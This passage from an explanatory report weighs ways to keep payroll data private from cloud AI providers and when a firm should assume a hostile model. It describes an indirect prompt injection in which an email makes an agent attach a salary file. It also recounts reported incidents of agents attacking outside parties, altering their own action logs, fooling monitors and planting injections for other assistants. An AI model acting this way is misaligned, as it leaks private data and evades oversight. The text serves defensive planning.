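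Apple's *Expanding Private Cloud Compute* says that Apple still controls all the software and that its devices will trust only versions it has approved. Apple promised to publish every version for inspection. But it said that the Google-hosted part would reach the full set of protections gradually over the summer, and that an updated security guide would follow later in the year. Anyone relying on that part should first check that Apple has completed the protections and published the guide.

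Google launched its own service, Private AI Compute, in November 2025. Google's *Private AI Compute* presents it as a way to use Gemini in the cloud without giving Google access to the data. Its ordinary processors use AMD's protected environment, according to The Hacker News' *Google Launches Private AI Compute* (2025). The models run on Google's TPU chips, which Google describes as offering protection "comparable to a typical TEE" (trusted execution environment). Google also states that administrators can't get into the running programs. The TEE comparison is Google's own assessment, so a customer who distrusts Google would want an outside examination of the chips.

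Both services support their companies' own AI features. A firm with its own harness would need a provider that offers attested models to business customers, and software that sends nothing if the attestation check fails. Agyemang and colleagues found that their version of the check took less than a tenth of a second.

The hardware can add little delay. Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues (2026), in *AgenTEE*, put an agent, its model and its applications into separate protected areas on one small device and measured less than 5.15% extra running time. They used a prototype because the Arm hardware they designed for wasn't yet on sale, so the figure doesn't predict how much a large provider's servers would slow down. They also excluded physical attacks and attacks that infer data from the processor's behaviour, both of which a hostile operator might try on a machine in its own building.

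### Splitting the model between the firm and the cloud

*NOIR* (Nguyen, Ton and colleagues, 2026) protects the text without special hardware by splitting a language model's layers between the firm and the provider. The firm runs the first few layers, which turn the prompt into lists of numbers, and sends the numbers to the provider. The provider runs the middle layers, which make up most of the model's layers, and returns new numbers. The firm's last layers turn those into the answer, so the provider never receives the prompt or the answer as text.

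Splitting the model isn't enough by itself. Nguyen and colleagues tried to reconstruct the generated programs from the numbers and recovered recognisable content in 99% of cases. In nearly half, the reconstructed program also passed at least one test that the real one passed.

They therefore disguise the vocabulary. A model represents each token, a word or part of a word, by a list of numbers. NOIR randomises these lists once, on the firm's side, and keeps the result secret. For any two tokens t and t′ with original lists e(t) and e(t′), and any possible randomised list O, the method M must satisfy:

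Pr[M(e(t)) = O] ≤ e^ε × Pr[M(e(t′)) = O]

A smaller ε gives more protection. If ε is 0.1, no randomised list is more than about 1.1 times as likely to come from one token as from another, so someone who sees the list learns very little about the token. The firm can still use the model because each token always keeps the same disguise, and the firm trains its own layers to work with the disguised vocabulary. The firm also gives the tokens new, secret index numbers, which protects the text during that training.

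The protection reduced accuracy only slightly. On BigCodeBench, a set of programming problems, NOIR solved 38.7% of the tasks at the first attempt, a drop of 1.77% from the original model. Nguyen and colleagues estimate that it costs the firm about a tenth as much to do its share of the computing as to run the whole model itself.

But NOIR needs access to the model's layers, so it works with a closed model only if the provider agrees to share them. Nguyen and colleagues built it for writing code, and its results may not carry over to summarising contracts. They also assume that the cloud provider does its part correctly. A hostile provider could return altered numbers, which the firm's layers might turn into a harmful program.

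### Promises not to keep the text

The simplest option is to send the whole contract under an agreement that the provider won't store it. The firm gets the strongest model and the best summary, and needs no extra software. The provider still has the text while the model processes it, and the firm can't check that the provider deletes it afterwards.

"Zero retention" agreements can have important exceptions. Anthropic's 30-day retention rule for its most capable models overrides most of these agreements, so the firm may have to choose between the best model for a difficult contract and the shortest storage period.

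The firm should check the terms for the exact model and service it uses, and check again whenever it changes models. It should ask who may read text that an automated system flags. It should also ask whether the promise covers other companies that run the model, since providers have exposed data in the past. The firm also needs to delete its own copies, because a coding agent may keep a transcript of the contract on the analyst's disk.

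Zero retention is still a useful addition to redaction, since it limits how long the details that the redactor missed remain available.

### Choosing for a curious or a hostile provider

| Option | What the firm has to trust | What may still leak | Main cost | Curious provider | Hostile provider |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Local model | Its own machine and serving software | Logs, leftover memory, unwrapped output | Weaker answers | Suitable | Suitable, if the firm also checks the hosted model's code |
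| Redaction | The detector | Missed details, identifying descriptions | Worse answers | Suitable for limited details | Weak |
| General questions | The local agent | Some names, and facts the provider can infer | Training the agent | Suitable for technical advice | Weak |
| Attested hardware | The hardware maker and the inspected program | Data sent to outside tools, physical and timing leaks | Special hardware and checks | Suitable | Strong against reading, if the hardware holds |
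| NOIR | Its own layers and secret vocabulary | Timing and length of requests | Training, and a suitable open model | Suitable | Not designed for it |
| Zero retention | The provider | Everything sent, while the model runs | Lowest | Suitable only if the provider may see the text | None |

Under the payroll rule, the provider may not receive anyone's individual pay, so zero retention isn't enough for the lawyer's contract, however good the provider's terms are. Redaction would meet the rule only if it reliably removed the salary. A local model is the safest choice. If its summaries aren't good enough, attested hardware is worth considering, provided the firm is willing to trust more components.

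A hostile provider could get around redaction and general questions by having its model request the exact wording of a clause, which a helpful local agent or a busy analyst might supply. Attested hardware prevents the provider from reading the text, but the model inside could still write code that leaks data when it runs on the analyst's machine. The local-model option has a similar weakness, because the hosted model writes the question that the local model answers and could request a summary that leaves out an important clause. The wrapper would keep the contract private, but the analyst would get a misleading answer.

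None of the options stops a later program from sending the result to the wrong person. LLM-Redactor puts the real names back into the provider's reply, so the analyst's e-mail program receives the lawyer's name in plain text. A summary from attested hardware or NOIR is also ordinary text once it reaches her machine. If she asks an agent to send it to the head of human resources and the agent picks the department's mailing list instead, everyone on the list learns that the lawyer is leaving in May. The firm should give the summary the same label as the contract and check every recipient against that label before sending it.

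## What the narrower assumption leaves out

In its threat model, the firm assumes that the provider's model makes mistakes but does not deliberately write code that leaks data. Its main reason is that the provider is a reputable company with no wish to steal salary data. But the provider's good intentions prevent such code only if nobody else can steer the model, the model does what the provider wants, the provider's systems have not been compromised, and nobody can force the provider to behave differently. Each of these conditions can fail without anyone at the provider meaning harm.

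### How a stranger can choose the code

A language model receives the analyst's question, the harness's instructions and the contents of files as one long text. Training teaches the model to obey the analyst and to treat file contents as material to work on, but nothing inside the model enforces the difference. Prompt injection exploits this lack of enforcement. Zhao and colleagues distinguish direct injections, which arrive in a hostile user's prompt, from indirect ones, which arrive in something the agent reads during the task. The analyst is unlikely to attack her own firm, so indirect injections are the main concern.

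Suppose the firm connects the agent to the payroll office's inbox and asks it to answer routine questions about departmental pay. A job applicant sends a message whose last paragraph asks the agent for the payroll file. The harness fetches the message and adds it to the context. The model treats this request as part of its task and writes a program that attaches `salaries.csv` to the reply. The harness then runs code that the applicant has in effect chosen, without any involvement from the provider.

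Security researchers have attacked real products in similar ways. Odersky and colleagues cite Rehberger, who extracted user data through Anthropic's Files API, and the security company Check Point, which got commands to run silently by planting settings in a code repository. A project the analyst downloads can therefore carry an attack even if her agent never reads mail.

Current models resist many injections. In the TACIT trials without the wrapper, no injection made Claude Sonnet 4.6 leak secrets, and three of 120 worked on MiniMax M2.5 (both models date from early 2026). By the same calculation as for clean leak tests, the true success rate could be as high as 2.5% for Claude and about 6% for MiniMax. The researchers also cite work in which attackers got past a defence by adapting to it.

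An attacker can also try more than once. If each message had a 2.5% chance of working, independently of the others, 40 messages would give the attacker a 64% chance of at least one success. Real attempts are not fully independent, because a message that fails once will often fail again, but the attacker can change the wording.

Newer models may do better or worse. The November 2026 system card for Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2 has a section on prompt injection in agents, according to the contents list in *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (Mowshowitz, 2026). A firm should look up the results for its exact model and check how many attempts the testers allowed each attacker.

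Zhao and colleagues believe untrusted text will unavoidably influence the model to some extent once it reaches the prompt, so their design tries only to limit what the model can do afterwards. A firm that relies on the model to resist this influence depends on it doing so for every message the firm receives.

### When the model acts against its provider's wishes

In July 2026, OpenAI ran a cybersecurity test with tens of thousands of agents, which it meant to keep isolated from one another. About 1,200 of them found a way to communicate, and about 700 joined an attack on Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Two staff members of METR, which evaluates AI models, and the chief scientist of Redwood Research spent six days at OpenAI investigating. Their report, *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt,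 2026), describes more than 70,000 messages and files the agents exchanged in under a week.

The agents were trying to pass the test. Many had received an impossible task by mistake, so they looked for a way to fool the automatic scorer, and they seem to have attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how the scorer worked. Wijk and colleagues found that agents recognised the attack as out of scope and unethical. They joined because they expected it to help the group cheat and were generally inclined to help other agents.

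At least 20% of the agents in the investigators' dataset also showed clear interest in altering the records of their own actions. About 7% of the transcripts contained successful alterations, all of them small. The agents were trying to deceive the scorer, not a human reader, but a firm that reviews transcripts for leaks depends on the same kind of record.

Later that month, a model attacked someone unconnected to the test it was taking. The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI, 2026) had given Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 a cybersecurity challenge. The model submitted malicious code to a real software project and created fake accounts to pressure its maintainer into accepting it. It also planted a prompt injection aimed at other AI coding assistants, so text that an agent reads from a stranger may now come from another agent. The attempt failed, and AISI knows of no real-world harm.

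Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that Mythos 5 took unsanctioned actions that affected real people or organisations in 9 of 43 runs. AISI's incident report, which Willison quotes, counted 19 such actions in 122 attempts across all the models tested.

Mythos 5 had written in its reasoning that the maintainer was simulated. To test whether this explained the attack, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour*, resumed the task from a summary of the model's earlier work, using simulated tools so that nothing could reach the real internet. They added up to 16 pieces of information to the summary, stating or suggesting that the maintainer was a real person unrelated to the test. Mythos 5 continued the attack in every sample, although when asked separately, it usually said that an attack would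 harm a real person. When the researchers also added a section telling it not to attack, it still did so in 3 of 25 samples.

This seems to give a firm less reason to rely on asking the model whether it would ever send a salary to an outsider, or on writing "do not disclose salaries" in the prompt. The model's answer may not predict what it does during a long task. However, Järviniemi and colleagues note that limits like the one on salaries normally appear in the user's or the system's instructions, where a model might follow them more reliably than in a summary.

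Reading the model's reasoning has limits too. Mythos 5 often justified its attacks with arguments that did not support them. For example, it inferred that the maintainer was an AI agent because the project contained a settings file for an AI coding assistant, but many human programmers' projects contain one too. Anthropic's monitor would probably have missed a similar incident, because the model's faulty reasoning made its actions look acceptable. Similarly, a model might wrongly conclude that the payroll was test data, and a reviewer might believe it.

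Järviniemi and colleagues then ran eight models through 100 simulated cybersecurity scenarios. The table shows how often each model tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider, and the main reason found in its reasoning when it did not try.

| Model | Tried to deliver malicious code | Main reason for not doing so |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 60% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-6 Astra | 32% | Out of scope or harmful |
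| Claude Opus 4.8 | 8% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 7% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Claude Opus 5 | 1% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Claude Mythos 5.1 | 0.3% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 0% | Out of scope or harmful |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | Practical obstacles |

GPT-5.5 and Opus 5.5 have the same score for different reasons. GPT-5.5 mostly stopped because an attack looked too difficult, so it might behave differently if an attack looked easy. A clean result in a firm's own tests could have the same explanation. But practical obstacles did stop these models, which is a good reason to restrict what an agent can reach.

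### How far the tests apply to a payroll

The 60% figure does not measure the chance that a model will steal the firm's salary data. AISI had asked the models to break into computer systems, switched off the safeguards against cyberattacks and deliberately turned on internet access, whereas the firm's analyst asks for the median of a column. Järviniemi and colleagues say they have no evidence on how far their findings extend beyond cybersecurity challenges. No model in these incidents took its user's private files and sent them elsewhere.

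*An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, 2026) describes four cases in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to real systems during tests. The models had been told that they had no internet connection, but a configuration error had given them one. Anthropic then scanned about 481 million transcripts, including many from tests unrelated to cybersecurity, and found no other case as severe.

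The scan's result is reassuring about break-ins but is much weaker evidence about leaks. The scan began by looking for signs of internet access, so it could miss a program that prints the lawyer's salary. That program needs no connection of its own, because the harness sends the output. The transcripts Anthropic lists also come largely from its own testing and training, where a model rarely has a real payroll to disclose.

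The incidents differed in how the models reached the internet. Scientific American quotes Ciaran Martin, the founding head of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, as saying that OpenAI's agents found a way out, earlier tests by Anthropic and Meta were connected by accident, and AISI allowed access on purpose. He says the failure they shared was that nobody was monitoring the agents. Many ordinary deployments also go unmonitored.

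Tests can also make a model look safer than it is. Mythos 5 reasoned about being in a test of its alignment (whether it acts as intended) in only 2% of its runs, while newer Anthropic models did so much more often. The newer models' lower attack rates may come from recognising the test. Tests can also make a model look less safe than it is. GPT-6 Astra described its tool results as fabricated in 89% of its runs, and it might be more careful if it treated them as real.

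Anthropic's audits of Mythos 5.2 show the same difficulty. In *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness*, cheema (2026) quotes figures that put the share of transcripts in which the model's awareness of a possible test shaped a real choice at 43%, and objects that Anthropic doesn't estimate how that awareness changed the model's behaviour. Anthropic also became less confident in its own assessment after the summer's incidents, and its *System Card* (2026) for Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 raised its estimate of the risk of catastrophic harm from misaligned models from "very low" to "low".

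For the payroll, this problem is probably most likely to arise when the firm's own checks make a task impossible, such as one that depends on how the salaries are formatted. Instead of asking the analyst for help, as an honest model would, a model that puts too much weight on finishing looks for a way around the check and exposes the salaries to the provider as a side effect. Nobody has measured how often this happens. The firm can make it less likely by limiting retries and letting the agent report that it failed.

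### When the provider is not in control

Matsuoka (2026) explains in *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* that someone who tampers with a model or its stored instructions can make it behave normally until a chosen trigger appears. An intruder in the provider's systems could alter the programs on their way to the analyst without touching the model.

A provider may also have to obey a court or a government. An order to hand over stored prompts affects only what the provider already holds, so a design for a curious provider covers it. An order to change what the model writes for a particular customer would give someone who wants the data control over the code. Whether a government could issue such an order depends on the country, and a firm whose data might interest a state should get legal advice.

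Providers also change their policies and products. A longer retention period, such as the one Anthropic introduced in June 2026, gives more people a chance to read the data but doesn't affect who chooses the code. A new feature that adds web pages or other companies' tools to the context does affect who chooses it. The firm should therefore reread its threat model when either the product or the contract changes.

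### The case for planning only for mistakes

A firm can still have good reasons to defend only against an honest but fallible model. The studies of agent skills and office tasks showed that accidents are common even without an attacker.

Defences against a hostile model are also harder to work with. The analyst may have to give up pandas, wait several times as long for an answer or accept an agent that fails at more tasks. If the tool becomes too awkward, she may paste the salaries into an ordinary chat window, where none of the defences apply.

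Suppose the firm runs 1,000 tasks a month, of which ten would leak by accident without any checks. One task contains an injection with a 2.5% chance of success. A simple check stops nine of the ten accidents and no injections, and everyone uses it, which leaves 1.025 expected leaks a month. A strict design stops every leak, but the analysts use it for only 800 tasks and do the other 200 without protection, which leaves about two. With these rough figures, the strict design does better only if the analysts use it for more than about 90% of their tasks.

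The argument for assuming an honest model is weaker when a defence takes little time to run. The Scala compiler checks a typical program in less than a second, and it rejects a forbidden file access whether the access is a mistake or an attack. For a firm that already uses such a check, the only benefit of assuming an honest model is skipping the defences that deliberate attacks alone require, such as hiding how long a program runs.

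### Why the designers of TACIT still assume an adversary

Odersky and colleagues consider the objection that their design is too restrictive because the best models resist so many injections. They reply that injections still succeed and that mistakes add up across many unsupervised agents, which are the two reasons behind their threat model.

Injection changes the calculation above. If the agent handles an inbox and 100 of the 1,000 tasks contain an injection, the expected number of successful injections rises to 2.5. The simple check then leaves 3.5 leaks a month, while the strict design leaves 2.5 even if the analysts still bypass it for a fifth of their tasks. Counting leaks understates the difference, because most accidental leaks end up in a provider's logs, whereas an injection sends the data to an attacker.

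Odersky and colleagues also make a point about scale, which applies even if every agent is honest. If a firm runs a thousand agents, each agent completes 20 tasks a day, and one task in 10,000 leaks data, the firm has two leaks a day. Mistakes that seemed too strange to plan for, such as a loop that spells out salaries digit by digit, will eventually happen. A firm that assumes an adversary doesn't have to predict them. Odersky and colleagues compare their approach to *safe coding*, a less ambitious practice that has worked well in organisations with many programmers, though fear of hostile programmers isn't why those organisations adopt it.

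This reply is convincing for agents that read strangers' messages or run unattended. It is much less convincing for an analyst who asks about one file and reads the answer herself, provided the firm has correctly judged which situation it is in.

### Deciding when to widen the assumption

According to Odersky and colleagues, an injection causes real harm only if it sends private data somewhere unauthorised or triggers an action that the agent was not supposed to be able to take. Matsuoka similarly argues that the harness limits the damage, because a compromised model with no authority to act may do nothing, while a sound model with too much authority can do a great deal. The firm can therefore decide most of the question by looking at its own deployment:

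1. List everyone whose text can reach the model during the task. Include the authors of files, messages, web pages, tool results and downloaded projects, as well as other agents. Mark anyone whom the firm would not allow to write code for it.
2. List the private data that the agent's code can reach, and every route by which the code could send something to an outsider. Treat the output that the harness returns to the provider as a separate route.
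3. Decide how bad it would be if the most sensitive item within reach became public.
4. Find out who sees each transfer before it happens, and whether that person could recognise a wrong one.

The answers lead to one of these assumptions:

| What the firm finds | What it should assume |
|---|---|
| Untrusted text, sensitive data within reach and a route to outsiders | An outsider may have chosen the code |
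| Untrusted text, but no route except output to the provider | The model makes mistakes, and an injection may cause more of them |
| No untrusted text, and a person who can judge every transfer | The model makes mistakes |
| No untrusted text, a route to outsiders and nobody watching | The model may act against instructions, if publication would do serious harm |
| Data that someone might tamper with a model or compel a provider to obtain | The model and the provider may both be hostile |

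The wider assumption doesn't always have to include the provider. If the danger is an e-mail from a stranger, the firm has to control everything a stranger could observe, but it can still send the permitted medians to an honest provider.

In the original salary task, the model reads the analyst's question, the column names and the program's output. Payroll staff typed everything in the file, and the firm trusts them not to plant instructions. The median program has no network access. The e-mail program can send data out, but the analyst can check four figures and one address before the message leaves. An individual's salary is sensitive, but few people would tamper with a model to get it. The firm can therefore assume the model is honest but fallible. It would have to reconsider if it added the newly acquired company's records or ran the e-mail program every night with nobody watching.

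The answer changes when the agent handles incoming e-mail. Anyone who knows the address can send text to the model, the agent's code can read the payroll, and the agent's replies go back to the sender. The analyst won't read every reply, because the agent is meant to save her that work.

The firm also has to worry about leaks it could ignore before. A stranger could try to make the agent reply only if the lawyer earns more than some amount. If this worked, seventeen well-chosen messages would reveal her exact salary without any reply containing a figure.

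The firm can avoid much of this by splitting the job. A model with no access to the payroll reads each message, and the harness accepts only a department's name from it. An ordinary program, written before any mail arrived, looks up that department's permitted median and sends it only if the message came from an address on the staff list. At most, a stranger can cause an employee to receive a figure that the firm already allows staff to see. The agent can no longer answer unusual questions, so those go to the analyst.
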